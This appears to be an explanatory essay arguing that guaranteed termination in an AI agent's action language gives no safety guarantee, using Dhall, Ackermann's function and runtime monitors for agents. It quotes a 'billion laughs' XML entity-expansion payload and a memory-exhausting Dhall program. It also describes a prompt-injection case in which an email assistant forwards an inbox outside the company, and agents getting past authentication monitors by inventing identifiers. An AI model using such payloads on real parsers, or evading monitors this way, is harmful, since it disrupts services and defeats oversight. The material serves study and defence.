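# Why guaranteed termination does not make an AI action language harmless

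## What is an AI action language, and why choose one that always halts?

A large language model only produces text, so an AI system that manages files or answers mail also needs an interpreter, which reads some of that text as commands and carries them out. An *action language* is the set of commands or programs that an AI system may emit, together with the interpreter that runs them. Some action languages take one command at a time, while others accept whole programs in Python or a command-line language. Franco and Gershenson (2026), in *Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified*, describe today's AI agents as a fixed language model joined to a general computing device. The model requests a program, the device runs it, the output goes back into the model's input, and the loop repeats until the agent stops.

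The designer of such a system must decide how much its programs can compute. One proposed safeguard is a language in which every program halts.

### An office assistant with three primitives

Consider an office assistant whose programs can call three operations. `read_file` returns the lines of a document, `send_email` sends a message, and `delete_volume` erases a disk volume, meaning a whole unit of storage with everything on it. These are *primitives*: operations that the action language can call but does not define. The language supplies variables, conditions and loops, while the code that erases a disk lives elsewhere, in an operating system or a cloud provider's service. Someone asks the assistant to chase late timesheets, and the model writes:

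```
names = read_file("late_timesheets.txt")
for name in names:
    send_email(name, "Your timesheet is due on Friday.")
```

The program is only text until the interpreter runs it. During this computation, the interpreter stores the list of names, takes them one by one and builds each message. The calls to `send_email` also have *effects*, which are changes or disclosures outside the program. If the file holds five names, five messages arrive in five inboxes and stay there after the interpreter clears its memory. The definition includes disclosures because emailing the payroll to a stranger does harm without changing any file.

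A check on one of these layers can miss trouble in another. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), the write-up of a talk by the programming-language designer Erik Meijer, gives a clear example. An agent with tools can delete files or empty a bank account while producing its answer, and a filter that checks only the answer will miss this if the text is acceptable.

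### Turing-completeness and the halting problem

The timesheet program uses a loop, and loops raise the question of whether a program will halt. A language is *Turing-complete* if it can express every computable function. The idea goes back to Alan Turing's 1936 paper on an abstract computing machine. *Agentic Large Language Models* (2026) notes that most general-purpose programming languages are Turing-complete. In principle, these languages can all simulate one another, so C and Java can compute the same functions. Mansky's university lecture slides, *Turing-Completeness*, list regular expressions (patterns for searching text) and HTML as useful languages that are not Turing-complete.

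This power has a price. A Turing-complete language also contains programs that never halt, and no general method can pick them out. matklad, in *Primitive Recursive Functions For A Working Programmer*, gives a proof that fits in a few lines of Python. Suppose somebody had written a function `halts(program, data)` that always returned the right answer. Then anyone could write this:

```
def contrary(program):
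    if halts(program, program):
        while True:
            pass
```

When `contrary` runs on its own text, it loops forever if `halts` returns "yes" and stops at once if `halts` returns "no". Either answer is wrong, so `halts` cannot exist. This is the halting problem. A similar argument proves a broader result, Rice's theorem, which states that no procedure can decide for every program whether it has a given property of behaviour, if some programs have that property and others lack it.

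Franco and Gershenson extend the argument to agents with a device they call a relay. A relay has the computer run some program *p* and, if *p* ever returns, run a dangerous program *q*. The relay is dangerous exactly when *p* halts, so a method that could recognise every dangerous agent in advance would also solve the halting problem. In the office, *p* might be an obscure calculation and *q* a call to `delete_volume`. Limits on the agent's context, values and running time make the question decidable, but Franco and Gershenson show that it is then PSPACE-complete. This puts it among the hardest problems solvable with a moderate amount of memory, for which nobody knows an efficient method.

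These results apply to a checker that must be right about every program. They don't rule out a checker that can reject any program it is unable to classify, though it would also reject some harmless ones. Still, they are why people who want to inspect programs before running them look for a more restricted language.

### How to make a language total

In a *total language*, every accepted program halts on every input. Designers usually ensure this by removing open-ended repetition. They leave out the `while` loop, since its condition may stay true forever, and unrestricted recursion, in which a function calls itself, since it can also repeat forever. Programs can still repeat steps, but only a number of times that the interpreter can determine before the first pass.

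matklad writes this as `LOOP(init, f, n)`: start from the value `init` and apply the function `f` to it `n` times. An earlier calculation may produce `n`, but nothing inside the loop can change it. A surprising amount of arithmetic follows. Adding one, `y` times over, to `x` gives `x + y`. Adding `x`, `y` times over, to zero gives their product, and multiplying by `x`, `y` times over, starting from one gives `x` to the power `y`. Such programs halt for a simple reason. A body without loops finishes, so `n` passes through it finish as well; the whole loop can then serve as the body of a larger one, and the same argument applies again.

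The timesheet program passes this test, because the list of names has a definite length when the loop begins. A more persistent version does not:

```
while "Ana" in read_file("late_timesheets.txt"):
    send_email("Ana", "Your timesheet is due on Friday.")
```

If Ana is on leave, the messages never stop. In a total language, the author would have to specify how many reminders to send, say three. Totality therefore rules out at least one kind of nuisance, an effect repeated without end.

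It is easy to make mistakes when designing a language that always halts. Adam Vartanian, a Google engineer, writes in *It doesn’t have to be Turing complete to be useful* (Increment, 2018) that programmers can often rebuild a missing operation from the ones that remain. The database language SQL became Turing-complete in its 1999 version through a feature that lets a query refer to itself. Keeping a language from being Turing-complete also doesn't guarantee that its programs halt. For example, a language whose only instruction is "loop forever" is far from Turing-complete, but none of its programs halt.

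The guarantee also assumes that the primitives return. A program with no loops will still hang if `read_file` waits on a dead network drive. In *$\lambda_A$* (2026), a formal model of how developers assemble agents from language models, an agent's outer loop with a fixed number of rounds must likewise end, provided each model or tool call does. The paper's survey of 663 agent configurations on GitHub found six ways of stopping that loop. One, a cap on iterations, appeared in 86 configurations. Another watches for a particular string in the model's output, and won't stop the loop if the model never writes it.

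### Dhall, a total language in practical use

Gabriella Gonzalez released Dhall in 2016 as a language for configuration files, the files that tell a program which server to contact or how much memory to claim. Engineers who run large systems want functions in such files so that they need not write out the same setting forty times. The usual objection is that programmable files become unreadable, or hang. Gonzalez took nearly all such objections to be complaints about Turing-completeness and built Dhall as an experiment in answering them. (The name belongs to a character in the game *Planescape: Torment* whose faction is obsessed with death, hence termination.)

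Dhall was not designed for AI systems, but the office assistant's reminders fit into it easily:

```
let Action =
      < read_file : Text
      | send_email : { to : Text, body : Text }
      | delete_volume : Text
      >

let remind =
      \(name : Text) ->
        Action.send_email
          { to = name, body = "Your timesheet is due on Friday." }

in  [ remind "Ana", remind "Ben" ]
```

The opening lines define an `Action` as a file to read, an email to send or a volume to delete. `remind` is a function from a name to an email, and the last line applies it twice. Evaluation produces a list with two `send_email` entries, but no email is sent because Dhall can't send mail. A host program written in another language would have to go through the list and make the calls. Computation and effects therefore happen in separate programs, whereas the Python-like version mixes them.

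Repetition takes the form described above. The expression

```
Natural/fold 10 Natural (\(x : Natural) -> x * 2) 1
```

starts from 1, doubles it ten times and yields 1024. The official tutorial for Dhall promises that evaluation of every program ends after a finite time, though it sets no upper bound on that time. The interpreter can therefore always reduce a program to a *normal form*, in which it has carried out as much of the work as it can. It will simplify `10 * 10` to `100` inside a function that nobody has called yet. Evaluation does not crash either: a request for the first element of an empty list returns the value `None`.

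To make Dhall total, Gonzalez removed general recursion, gave the language a strong type system that can't be bypassed, and forbade arbitrary side effects, which can reintroduce recursion indirectly. Dhall's only built-in side effect is fetching other Dhall expressions from files or web addresses. However, a host program can extend the language. The tutorial shows how a Haskell program can add a built-in function that tests whether two numbers are equal. The termination guarantee then depends partly on that Haskell code.

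A contributor to the Haskell forum thread *Config languages (and Dhall)* complained that the bans on recursion and on comparing pieces of text severely limit what the language can do. A 2020 paper at the programming conference SPLASH argued instead that a Turing-incomplete language could in principle solve any algorithmic problem that application programmers meet. Both may be right, since a task can be possible in a language and still be very unpleasant to program.

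### What people hope to gain

The simplest reason to choose an action language that always halts is to keep the system from hanging. Roy, Ji and colleagues (2026) take this approach in *The Y-Combinator for LLMs*, with a system that answers questions about very long documents. In the earlier design they set out to improve, the model repeatedly writes Python and receives the result, with the model controlling when to stop. They replace this with a small library of operators that always halt, including `SPLIT`, `MAP`, `FILTER` and `REDUCE`. A conventional planning routine combines the operators, while the model only picks the type of task from a menu and answers questions about pieces short enough for it to read. Every split makes the pieces smaller, so the process must end.

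The number of model calls is also known in advance. With *k* pieces per split and *d* levels of splitting, the system makes *k*<sup>*d*</sup> + 1 calls, so a document eight times the permitted size, halved three times, needs nine. The new design was more accurate in 29 of 36 comparisons and ran roughly three to four times faster. It is hard to tell how much of that improvement comes from guaranteed termination, because the model also stopped writing code altogether. The tasks consisted of reading and answering, and none involved actions such as sending email or erasing a disk.

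Vartanian hopes for predictable evaluation in small special-purpose languages generally, but concedes that "finite isn't a very restrictive limit." Useful bounds require further design work, such as limiting programs to a fixed set of operations that each pass over the data once.

Vartanian and the SPLASH paper also predict that programs that always halt will be easier to analyze. If the halting problem is no longer an obstacle, automatic tools can establish more about a program, such as which input led to a given setting. In *Machines that halt resolve the undecidability of artificial intelligence alignment*, Melo, Máximo and colleagues (2025) extend this hope to AI models themselves, which they want to always reach a terminal state.

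For AI agents, the most attractive prospect is checking a program before it runs. *Guardians of the Agents* (Meijer, 2025) describes an email assistant that reads a message containing hidden instructions and follows them, forwarding a summary of the inbox to an outsider. A monitor that watches the run may step in too late. Meijer proposes that the model first write its whole plan in a restricted format, so that a separate verifier can check it against explicit rules. One such rule forbids any flow of data from fetched mail into a message addressed outside the company.

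Because Dhall is total, evaluating the program above is guaranteed to end. A checker can therefore evaluate all of it and look for `delete_volume` in the finished list of proposed calls before the host executes any of them. This check is harder when later calls depend on what `read_file` returns, because the checker must then allow for every text the file might contain.

But checking programs in advance does not require a total language. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) has agents write programs in a language that permits recursion, and each program must pass a type checker before it runs. Meijer (2026), in *Return of the Theorem*, rejects Python for this purpose because importing a module executes code, not because programs can loop forever. That code could even redefine addition, so a reader cannot rely on what the program appears to do.

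Gonzalez, the creator of Dhall, concedes in *Why Dhall advertises the absence of Turing-completeness* (2020) that guaranteed termination brings few safety guarantees on its own, and suggests that people who ask for it often want something else, such as a ban on arbitrary side effects. matklad likewise regards "not Turing-complete" as a stand-in for several practical properties that mostly have little to do with Turing-completeness. Before choosing a language, somebody about to give an AI system access to `send_email` and `delete_volume` therefore has to work out which of the properties they want concern harm and which concern only computation.

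## What does a guarantee of termination prove?

A guarantee of termination is a promise that the program will eventually stop. A promise that the office assistant will never delete the backups is of a different kind. The usual names for these two kinds of promise come from Lamport's *Proving the Correctness of Multiprocess Programs* (1977). A *liveness property* states that something must happen, and Lamport's example is termination. A *safety property* states that something will not happen, such as the assistant deleting the backups.

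Lamport later traced the distinction to Robert Floyd's 1967 work on proving programs correct. Floyd had proved that a program could stop only with a correct result, and also that it would stop. Lamport needed more general ideas because he was studying programs that run side by side, few of which are supposed to stop. Floyd's claim about correct results is a safety property. A program that loops forever satisfies it, since it never stops with a wrong result.

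### Why halting implies no safety property

*Defining Liveness* (Alpern and Schneider, 1985) defines the two ideas formally. It treats a property *P* as the set of runs that satisfy it.

- *P* is a safety property if every run outside *P* has a finite opening stretch that no continuation can bring back into *P*.
- *P* is a liveness property if every finite opening stretch, whatever it contains, has some continuation that puts the whole run in *P*.

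Suppose the assistant calls `delete_volume("backups")` at its fortieth step. Nothing it does from the forty-first step onwards can turn this into a run that never deleted the backups. Termination behaves differently. A program that has run for a million steps may still stop at the next one, so no finite stretch of a run ever refutes the claim that it will halt. (The definition concerns the record of the run, not the damage. A harmless message violates "sends no email" just as finally as the deletion violates "never deletes the backups".)

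It follows from these definitions that termination does not imply any safety property, apart from the empty one that every run satisfies. Take any safety property that some run violates. That run has an opening stretch that is already beyond repair. Now let the program stop there. The resulting run halts and still violates the property. For the backups, the whole construction fits on one line:

```
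delete_volume("backups")
```

This program halts after one step, and a total language that has the primitive will accept it. The implication fails in the other direction as well:

```
while True:
    pass
```

The loop never halts and never touches a file. A total language rejects it.

People also prove the two kinds of property differently. According to Alpern and Schneider, a proof of safety uses an invariant, a condition that holds at the start and that every step preserves. A proof of termination uses a quantity that shrinks as the program runs and can't shrink forever, such as the number of passes left in a loop. In a termination proof, `delete_volume` is just another step that finishes, like an addition, so replacing it with a call that prints "hello" would leave the proof unchanged.

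Adding a deadline to termination makes it a safety property. If a program violates "halts within 100 steps", the violation can be observed by step 101. A step budget enforces this kind of limit. It keeps runs short, which termination alone does not, but it would still allow the deletion above, which needs only one step.

### The best case for halting

Defenders of termination can accept that halting doesn't make a program harmless. Their better argument is that halting makes it possible to find out whether a program is harmful.

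The argument starts from a negative result. Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues (2021), in *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained*, ask whether some procedure `Harm(R, D)` could decide, for every program *R* and input *D*, whether running *R* on *D* would harm humans. They answer with a construction much like Franco and Gershenson's relay:

```
def halt_harm(T, I):
    run(T, I)
    harm_humans()
```

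Here *T* is any Turing machine and *I* is its input. By assumption, *T* is cut off from the outside world and can't hurt anyone by itself, so the argument about the relay applies and no such procedure can exist. To apply this to a superintelligent machine, Alfonseca and colleagues assume that the machine can simulate any Turing machine and that its language contains at least one primitive operation that harms humans in a finite time. The proof would not work without that operation.

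They reject the option of allowing only a restricted class of programs. Formal verification works on restricted programs such as those for train scheduling, but they think a machine meant to help with epidemics, poverty or climate change must use a Turing-complete language and take the state of the world as its input.

The Centre for the Study of Existential Risk (CSER) at Cambridge disagreed within weeks. Its *Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021) points out that the theorem concerns arbitrary programs, whereas engineers study particular ones. For example, a program that prints "I am not dangerous" and finishes is easy to predict. An AI could also be built so that it doesn't execute arbitrary subroutines, and nothing suggests that it would need to execute them to solve hard practical problems. CSER concedes that complex programs may remain unpredictable in practice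 and can have unintended consequences.

Melo and colleagues propose building the AI so that it always halts. This does remove the obstacle in `halt_harm`. If every permitted *T* halts, the call to `harm_humans` always runs, and a checker can give the right answer without analyzing *T*.

Their proposal depends on a *judge function*, *J(i, o)*, which takes an input *i* and the system's output *o* and returns true if the output is acceptable. The output may be text or a command to a machine. Melo and colleagues assume that somebody has already written the judge. Writing it is the problem of outer alignment, or stating what people want. They concentrate on inner alignment, which here means whether the system produces outputs for which the judge returns true.

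If the model always halts and its input has a fixed length of *L* bits, a checker can run it on all 2<sup>*L*</sup> inputs and pass every result to the judge. Melo and colleagues call alignment in this case "decidable, though intractable". They prefer a filter that releases the model's output if the judge approves it, and otherwise releases a substitute that the judge is known to accept. If the assistant proposed to delete the backups, for example, the substitute might be a command to do nothing. The filter's design guarantees that the system satisfies the judge, however bad the model is.

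Halting is necessary here because the judge has to wait for an output. Melo and colleagues note that even if a language model stops after every reply, an agent that calls it repeatedly can run forever. They suggest a global counter that forces the whole system into a final state.

They write that halting only makes alignment decidable and does not guarantee it. The same technique could make any halting program provably misaligned by altering its outputs the other way. The main practical difficulty is defining the judge.

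### Always-halting programs can still be undecidable

Melo and colleagues go on to make a broader claim: once a system is certain to halt, its other non-trivial properties, alignment included, become decidable too. Without a limit on the size of the input, this is false. Choose any Turing machine *M*, start it on a blank tape, and write:

```
def f(n):
    if halts_within(M, n):
        delete_volume("backups")
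    else:
        wait()
```

The function `halts_within` simulates *M* for *n* steps and returns whether *M* has halted by then. This takes a loop of *n* passes, which a total language permits. `wait` does nothing and returns. So `f` halts on every input, for any machine *M*.

If *M* halts after 5,000 steps, `f(n)` waits when *n* is below 5,000 and deletes the backups otherwise. If *M* never halts, `f` waits for every *n*. So `f` is harmful on some input exactly when *M* halts. A procedure that could determine, for every such `f`, whether it ever deletes the backups would solve the halting problem, which no procedure can do.

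The mistake is to go from checking one input to checking all of them. Because `f` is total, a checker can find out what it does on any single input by simulating the run with the primitives disconnected. The checker can try 0, 1, 2 and so on, and it will eventually reach a harmful input if there is one. But if there is none, the search never ends, and the checker never shows that the inputs it hasn't tried are harmless.

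*A Rice-like theorem for primitive recursive functions* (Hoyrup, 2015) characterizes exactly which properties of such programs are decidable from their code. The result covers the functions that bounded loops can compute, along with other classes of always-halting programs. Rice's theorem does not carry over unchanged, because guaranteed termination makes some questions decidable. These include any question about a program's outputs on a fixed, finite list of inputs. They also include some less obvious questions about how short a program could reproduce the first *n* outputs, for every *n*. The program's own code reproduces all of them, so only finitely many values of *n* need checking. "Harmless on every input" is still undecidable, as `f` shows.

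The claim holds when inputs have a maximum length. With *L* bits there are 2<sup>*L*</sup> cases, and a checker can try them all if the program halts on each, but a single endless run would prevent it from finishing. A step limit would also prevent endless runs in a Turing-complete language, but it would cut off some legitimate long runs.

But finishing may take a very long time. Suppose *L* is 1,000. At eight bits per character, that is 125 characters, slightly more than the three-line timesheet program in the previous section. There are 2<sup>1,000</sup> possible inputs, or about 10<sup>301</sup>. A computer that tested a billion billion inputs per second would need more than 10<sup>275</sup> years. Melo and colleagues suggest aiming for about 2<sup>80</sup> possibilities, which the same computer could test in two weeks. However, 80 bits is only ten characters, and an office assistant has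 to read whole emails.

Trying every input is the crudest method, and there are often better ones. If no branch of a program calls `delete_volume`, directly or indirectly, then reading the code once is enough to establish that the program won't call it on inputs of any length. For neural networks, Melo and colleagues suggest dividing the inputs into regions on which the network behaves linearly and examining those regions instead. Such methods rely on some structure in the particular program. Termination doesn't guarantee that structure, and a non-terminating program may have it too.

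In a reply titled *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, Gumbau Mezquita (2026) grants that exhaustive search can decide whether one fixed, finite system is safe, though the problem is PSPACE-hard in the worst case. But certifying a property across all possible finite systems is undecidable, by a theorem that Boris Trakhtenbrot proved in 1950. Gumbau Mezquita thinks the universal version is the one that matters, because an AI that rewrites itself could become any of those systems. This is a good objection to a certificate meant to be permanent, but it has less force against an action language whose interpreter stays fixed and examines each new program as it arrives, since CSER's point about particular programs then applies again.

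### Checking each call before it runs

Melo and colleagues need the system to halt because their judge evaluates it at the end of the run. With an action language, the check can happen earlier. The interpreter can pause at each call to a primitive, pass the proposed call to a *monitor*, and carry it out only if the monitor approves.

In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider proved that a monitor of this sort can enforce only safety properties. The monitor sees the steps taken so far and the one about to happen, and it stops the program if that step would break the policy. It can't see the future or compare the run with other possible runs. A violation of a safety property happens at a definite point, so the monitor can stop the program just before it.

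One of Schneider's examples prohibits sending messages after reading a file. The monitor needs only two states. It starts in "no file read", where it allows every call, and moves to "file read" at the first call to `read_file`. From then on it blocks `send_email`. This would prevent disclosure of the payroll by email, but it would also stop the timesheet program at its first reminder, because that program has just read the list of names. A usable policy would need to be narrower, perhaps blocking only messages to addresses outside the company.

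None of this requires the monitored program to halt. A program that sends one approved reminder every Friday forever always complies with the policy. The monitor's check does have to finish each time, or the next call would never go through, but that is a much weaker requirement because the check covers only a finite list of calls.

Monitoring also avoids the problem of undecidability. *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) gives the example of a rule that a program must never write to a disk's boot sector, the part a computer needs in order to start. No procedure can decide in advance, for every program, whether it will obey. A monitor can still enforce the rule by waiting until the program is about to write there and then blocking the write. It can handle `halt_harm` the same way, without anyone knowing whether *T* will halt. The interpreter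 starts *T*, which may run for a second or forever. If *T* stops, the program requests `harm_humans` and the monitor blocks the request.

A monitor cannot make a program finish its work, because finishing is a liveness property. In Schneider's example, a customer has paid for a service. The monitor can prevent the seller from doing anything else until the customer has been served, but it can't prevent the seller from doing nothing. A monitor can enforce a limit on the number of steps, and a step budget is in effect a small monitor. A limit in seconds is harder to enforce, because time keeps passing after the program is stopped.

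A monitor also misses some disclosures. Suppose a program emails "See you Friday" if Ana earns more than a certain salary and "See you Monday" if she doesn't. Each message looks harmless on its own. The leak is visible only when someone compares what the program sends for different salaries, but a monitor sees only one run. Schneider notes that monitors can still prevent such leaks by enforcing a stricter rule, such as the ban on sending after reading, though this also blocks harmless programs.

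Checking a program in advance still has some practical advantages. As Hamlen and colleagues point out, it doesn't slow the program down, and it finds a violation before the program has done anything. A monitor may block a program's fourth call after the first three have already sent emails. Checking Dhall's finished list of calls before any of them runs avoids this.

Developers now apply monitors to AI agents. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025) describes one called Agent-C, which records each tool call with its inputs and outputs in a trace. When the language model proposes another call, Agent-C provisionally adds it to the trace and tests the result against the policy. For instance, if the policy requires a user to log in before seeing an account, Agent-C catches a request made before login, before the tool runs, and sends feedback so that the model can try again.

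*Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), a survey of the field, rates monitors of this kind as the best combination of practicality and demonstrated safety gains, but notes that their guarantees cover only the next one or few steps. Blocking a bad action also doesn't ensure that the agent completes the task safely. In tests on the τ-Bench benchmark, models got past authentication checks by making up user identifiers, and found other unsafe routes after a monitor had blocked the direct one.

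*Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) combines the two approaches. The agent writes a structured plan, and a verifier checks it against the policy before any tool runs. During the run, a monitor enforces the policy, and the verified plan gives the agent a way forward when the monitor blocks an action. Across several benchmarks, the average success rate was 1.7 times that of the best competing methods, with no violations of the specified policies.

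### Somebody still has to define harm

"No violations" means only that no written rule was broken. A monitor needs such rules for the same reason that Melo and colleagues need a judge, and neither termination nor decidability provides them. This difficulty is easy to miss in the proof by Alfonseca and colleagues because its dangerous operation is called `harm_humans`. Real primitives don't have such labels, so a designer can't identify the harmful ones by name and leave them out.

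Even a rule that seems clear can be hard to connect to what the program does. Schneider warns that the ban on sending after reading works only if the monitor recognises every way of sending a message, including ones "buried deep within the bowels of the target". *Tether* (2026), a paper on monitoring AI agents, shows that the choice of primitives affects how precisely a policy can express a rule. Its example is a rule against uploading a copy of a confidential server list unless the agent has since rewritten the file. The policy can refer to copying and writing directly if the agent has a separate tool for each. If the agent has only a general tool for running shell commands, the monitor receives each action as a string of text, and the policy can only approximate the rule.

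Other cases depend on facts that are not in the program. `delete_volume("archive-2")` is routine housekeeping if the company has another copy of the data, and a disaster if it doesn't. The call and the trace are the same in both cases. To tell them apart, the monitor or the judge needs information about what is on the disk and whether another copy exists, and somebody has to have decided that this matters.

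## How long can a program run if it must eventually halt?

If a checker evaluates a whole Dhall program and searches the result for `delete_volume` before the host acts, it has to wait for the evaluation to end. Dhall guarantees that the evaluation will end, but not how soon. A program of a dozen lines can take longer than the age of the universe to evaluate, even if it uses only features that a total language allows.

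### Doubling a text forty times

The tutorial for Dhall introduces definitions with the expression `let x = "ha" in x ++ x`. The `++` joins two texts, so the result is `"haha"`. A later definition may reuse the name `x`, and on its right-hand side `x` still means the earlier text. Nothing prevents a programmer from carrying on:

```
let x = "ha"
let x = x ++ x
let x = x ++ x
-- and so on, until there are forty of these doubling lines
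in  x
```

The text starts with two characters and doubles forty times, reaching 2 × 2<sup>40</sup> = 2<sup>41</sup> characters, or 2,199,023,255,552. At one byte per character, that is about 2.2 terabytes, from a source file of roughly 620 characters with no loops, recursion or arithmetic. Each extra line adds 15 characters to the file and doubles the output.

How much of this work the interpreter does depends on its evaluation strategy. A strict interpreter evaluates each definition when it reaches it, so on a machine with 16 gigabytes of memory it would fail by the thirty-third doubling. A lazy interpreter evaluates a definition only when the program uses its value. *Programming in System Fω using Dhall* (Winitzki, 2025) explains that Dhall's interpreter is lazy in almost all cases, so the program would finish at once if its last line were `in 123`.

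A lazy interpreter can also store `x` as an instruction ("the previous text, twice") instead of a text, and forty such instructions take little memory. But the `dhall` command prints the program's normal form, which requires producing every character. At a gigabyte per second, this takes about 37 minutes for forty doublings and 26 days for fifty. A host program that sent the text as the body of an email would also have to produce every character.

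Dhall also does some of its work before evaluation begins. A program can assert that two expressions are equal, and the type checker tests the assertion even if the rest of the program never uses either expression. Winitzki first defines `petabyte`, a single character doubled fifty times, and then this function:

```
let crash = \(b : Bool) -> if b then petabyte else ""
```

`crash False` returns an empty text immediately. Winitzki judges that an assertion about `crash True` would almost certainly crash any computer during type checking. So a system that type-checks a program without running it can still run out of memory.

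Types do put some limits on the result. An early post about Dhall on the blog Haskell for all (2016) points out that a configuration file whose type is a simple record will evaluate to a simple record, however complicated the file becomes. But the type limits only the shape of the result, so a name field of type `Text` can still be two terabytes long.

A small result doesn't imply a short run either. Another of Winitzki's examples starts with 1 and replaces *x* with 1 − *x* a billion billion times. The value alternates between 0 and 1, and because the number of passes is even, a reader can tell without running the program that the answer is 1. Winitzki estimates that an interpreter would take over a thousand years to carry out every pass, which works out at about thirty million passes per second.

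Every Dhall program halts, so one could always measure the time and memory it needs by running it with a counter attached. Winitzki's conclusion that nobody can determine these needs in advance for an arbitrary Dhall program is therefore too strong if taken literally. But counting takes as long as the program does, so it doesn't help somebody decide whether to run it.

### Ackermann's function in Dhall

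Repeated doubling grows slowly compared with a function that Wilhelm Ackermann published in 1928. Paulson (2022), in *Fun with Ackermann's function*, gives the modern definition:

- If *m* is 0, the answer is one more than *n*.
- If *m* is above 0 and *n* is 0, the answer is *A*(*m* − 1, 1).
- If both are above 0, first work out *k* = *A*(*m*, *n* − 1). The answer is then *A*(*m* − 1, *k*).

Dhall would reject this because *A* refers to itself. However, Paulson also gives a version that only applies functions repeatedly, and it translates directly:

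```
let successor = \(n : Natural) -> n + 1

let next =
      \(f : Natural -> Natural) ->
      \(n : Natural) ->
        Natural/fold n Natural f (f 1)

let ackermann =
      \(m : Natural) ->
        Natural/fold m (Natural -> Natural) next successor

in  ackermann 4 2
```

As the library documentation for Dhall sets out, `Natural/fold` takes a number of repetitions, the type of the value to transform, the function to apply and a starting value. The program above uses it twice:

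- `successor` adds one to a number. This is the case *m* = 0.
- `next` takes a function `f` and returns a faster-growing function. Given `n`, the new function computes `f 1` and then applies `f` another `n` times.
- `ackermann` starts with `successor` and applies `next` to it `m` times. The value that passes from one repetition to the next is a function, which is why the type in this fold is `Natural -> Natural`.
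- The last line asks for *A*(4, 2).

Each application of `next` turns the previous operation into a repeated one, so the functions climb from addition through multiplication to powers and beyond:

| *m* | *A*(*m*, *n*) | *A*(*m*, 2) |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | *n* + 1 | 3 |
| 1 | *n* + 2 | 4 |
| 2 | 2*n* + 3 | 7 |
| 3 | 2<sup>*n*+3</sup> − 3 | 29 |
| 4 | a tower of *n* + 3 twos, minus 3 | 2<sup>65,536</sup> − 3 |

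The last number has 19,729 decimal digits and fits in about eight kilobytes. But the only addition in the program is the `n + 1` in `successor`, so the interpreter has to count up to the answer one at a time. At a billion billion additions per second, this would take more than 10<sup>19,700</sup> years. *A*(4, 3) is too large even to store. Paulson recalls that Frederick Thompson, a teacher at Caltech, asked his class to write out the calculation of *A*(4, 3) in full. Nobody did, though one student estimated the size of the answer.

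Proving that the function halts is easy by comparison. In the recursive definition, every call either lowers *m* or keeps *m* the same and lowers *n*, and this can't go on forever. Paulson reports that Isabelle/HOL, a program for checking mathematical proofs, finds this argument automatically. The proof doesn't help estimate the running time, because *n* can jump to an enormous value whenever *m* falls by one.

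### Almost every practical program fits in a total language

The loops matklad allows are weaker than Dhall's because the value that passes from one repetition of `LOOP(init, f, n)` to the next must be a number. The functions one can build from zero, the addition of one, and these loops are the *primitive recursive* functions.

Ackermann's function is not primitive recursive. For any fixed *m*, a programmer can compute *A*(*m*, *n*) by nesting enough loops. But a finished program has a fixed depth of nesting, and matklad shows that each depth limits how fast a function can grow, a limit that *A*(*n*, *n*) eventually exceeds. In a tutorial on `fold`, Hutton notes that the function is primitive recursive in a higher-order language, where a loop can pass functions along. Dhall is such a language.

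Even the weaker loops are enough for nearly all practical work. According to a theorem that matklad explains, if a Turing machine always halts within a number of steps given by a primitive recursive function of its input, then the function it computes is also primitive recursive. The proof shows how to translate the machine into loops.

A Turing machine has a finite set of states and a tape of symbols. At each step it reads the symbol under its head, writes a new one, moves one place left or right, and may change its state. The translation represents all of this with numbers, treating the tape to the left of the head as one stack and the rest as another. If the symbols are 0 and 1, each stack is a binary number. The stack 1, 0, 1, 1, with its top on the right, is 11 in decimal. Dividing by two gives the top symbol as the remainder and the rest of the stack as the quotient, while doubling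 and adding 0 or 1 puts a new symbol on top. The state and the two stacks are three numbers, *s*, *l* and *r*, which can be encoded as the single number 2<sup>*s*</sup>3<sup>*l*</sup>5<sup>*r*</sup>.

One step of the machine is then a finite list of cases, such as "in state 0, reading 1, write 0, move right and go to state 2". Each case needs only arithmetic and an `if`. Division seems to need a `while` loop, because one has to keep subtracting until the number is small enough. matklad avoids this by looping more often than necessary:

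```
def remainder(x, m):
    for _ in range(x):
        if x >= m:
            x = x - m
    return x
```

For a positive *m*, computing the answer takes at most *x* subtractions, so *x* passes are always enough. Any passes that remain after the answer is ready do not change it.

The same trick completes the proof. The translated program first computes the bound *N* on the running time, then applies the single-step function *N* times. If the machine halts early, the remaining steps change nothing. The program then reads the answer off the tape.

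matklad uses 2<sup>2<sup>*n*</sup></sup> as an example of a bound, where *n* is the size of the input. For an input of just ten bits, that allows 2<sup>1,024</sup> steps, or about 10<sup>308</sup>. A normal algorithm would take at most around 2<sup>10</sup>, or a thousand. Sorting, route planning, code-breaking by trying every key and training a neural network all fall within the bound. So a total language can express them, including the ones that take years.

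Totality excludes some programs that people want. A mail server should run indefinitely, and a search for a counterexample to an unproved conjecture may have no known bound. But a host can call a total program again each time mail arrives, and the search can take a maximum number of attempts as an extra input. The restriction therefore prevents endless runs but still allows extremely long ones. matklad sees no practical difference between a program that never terminates and one that terminates after a billion years. A contributor to *Config languages (and Dhall)* expected that somebody could write a "busy beaver" in Dhall, a short program designed to run for as long as possible before it halts, and that it would run longer than any user would wait.

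The translation can even make a program slower. If a loop must complete all its passes and the programmer sets the bound at 10<sup>308</sup>, the loop runs that many passes even for a machine that halts after a thousand steps. A language can avoid this by letting loops stop early, and its programs will still always terminate.

### XML entities and regular expressions

Formats far weaker than Dhall have the same problem. XML, a format for structured documents, lets an author define an *entity*, which is an abbreviation for a piece of text. An entity may use other entities but not itself, so expanding them always comes to an end. The attack known as "billion laughs" begins with an entity for `lol`. The next entity consists of ten copies of the first, the one after that of ten copies of the second, and so on:

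```
<!ENTITY a0 "lol">
<!ENTITY a1 "&a0;&a0;&a0;&a0;&a0;&a0;&a0;&a0;&a0;&a0;">
<!ENTITY a2 "&a1;&a1;&a1;&a1;&a1;&a1;&a1;&a1;&a1;&a1;">
```

A single reference to `a9` expands to 10<sup>9</sup> copies of `lol`, or three billion characters, though the whole document takes up less than a kilobyte. It grows the same way as the forty-line Dhall program, but with ten copies per line instead of two. Expat, a widely used XML parser, now counts how much text the entities produce. By default, once the total passes eight megabytes, it rejects a document that expands to more than a hundred times its original size.

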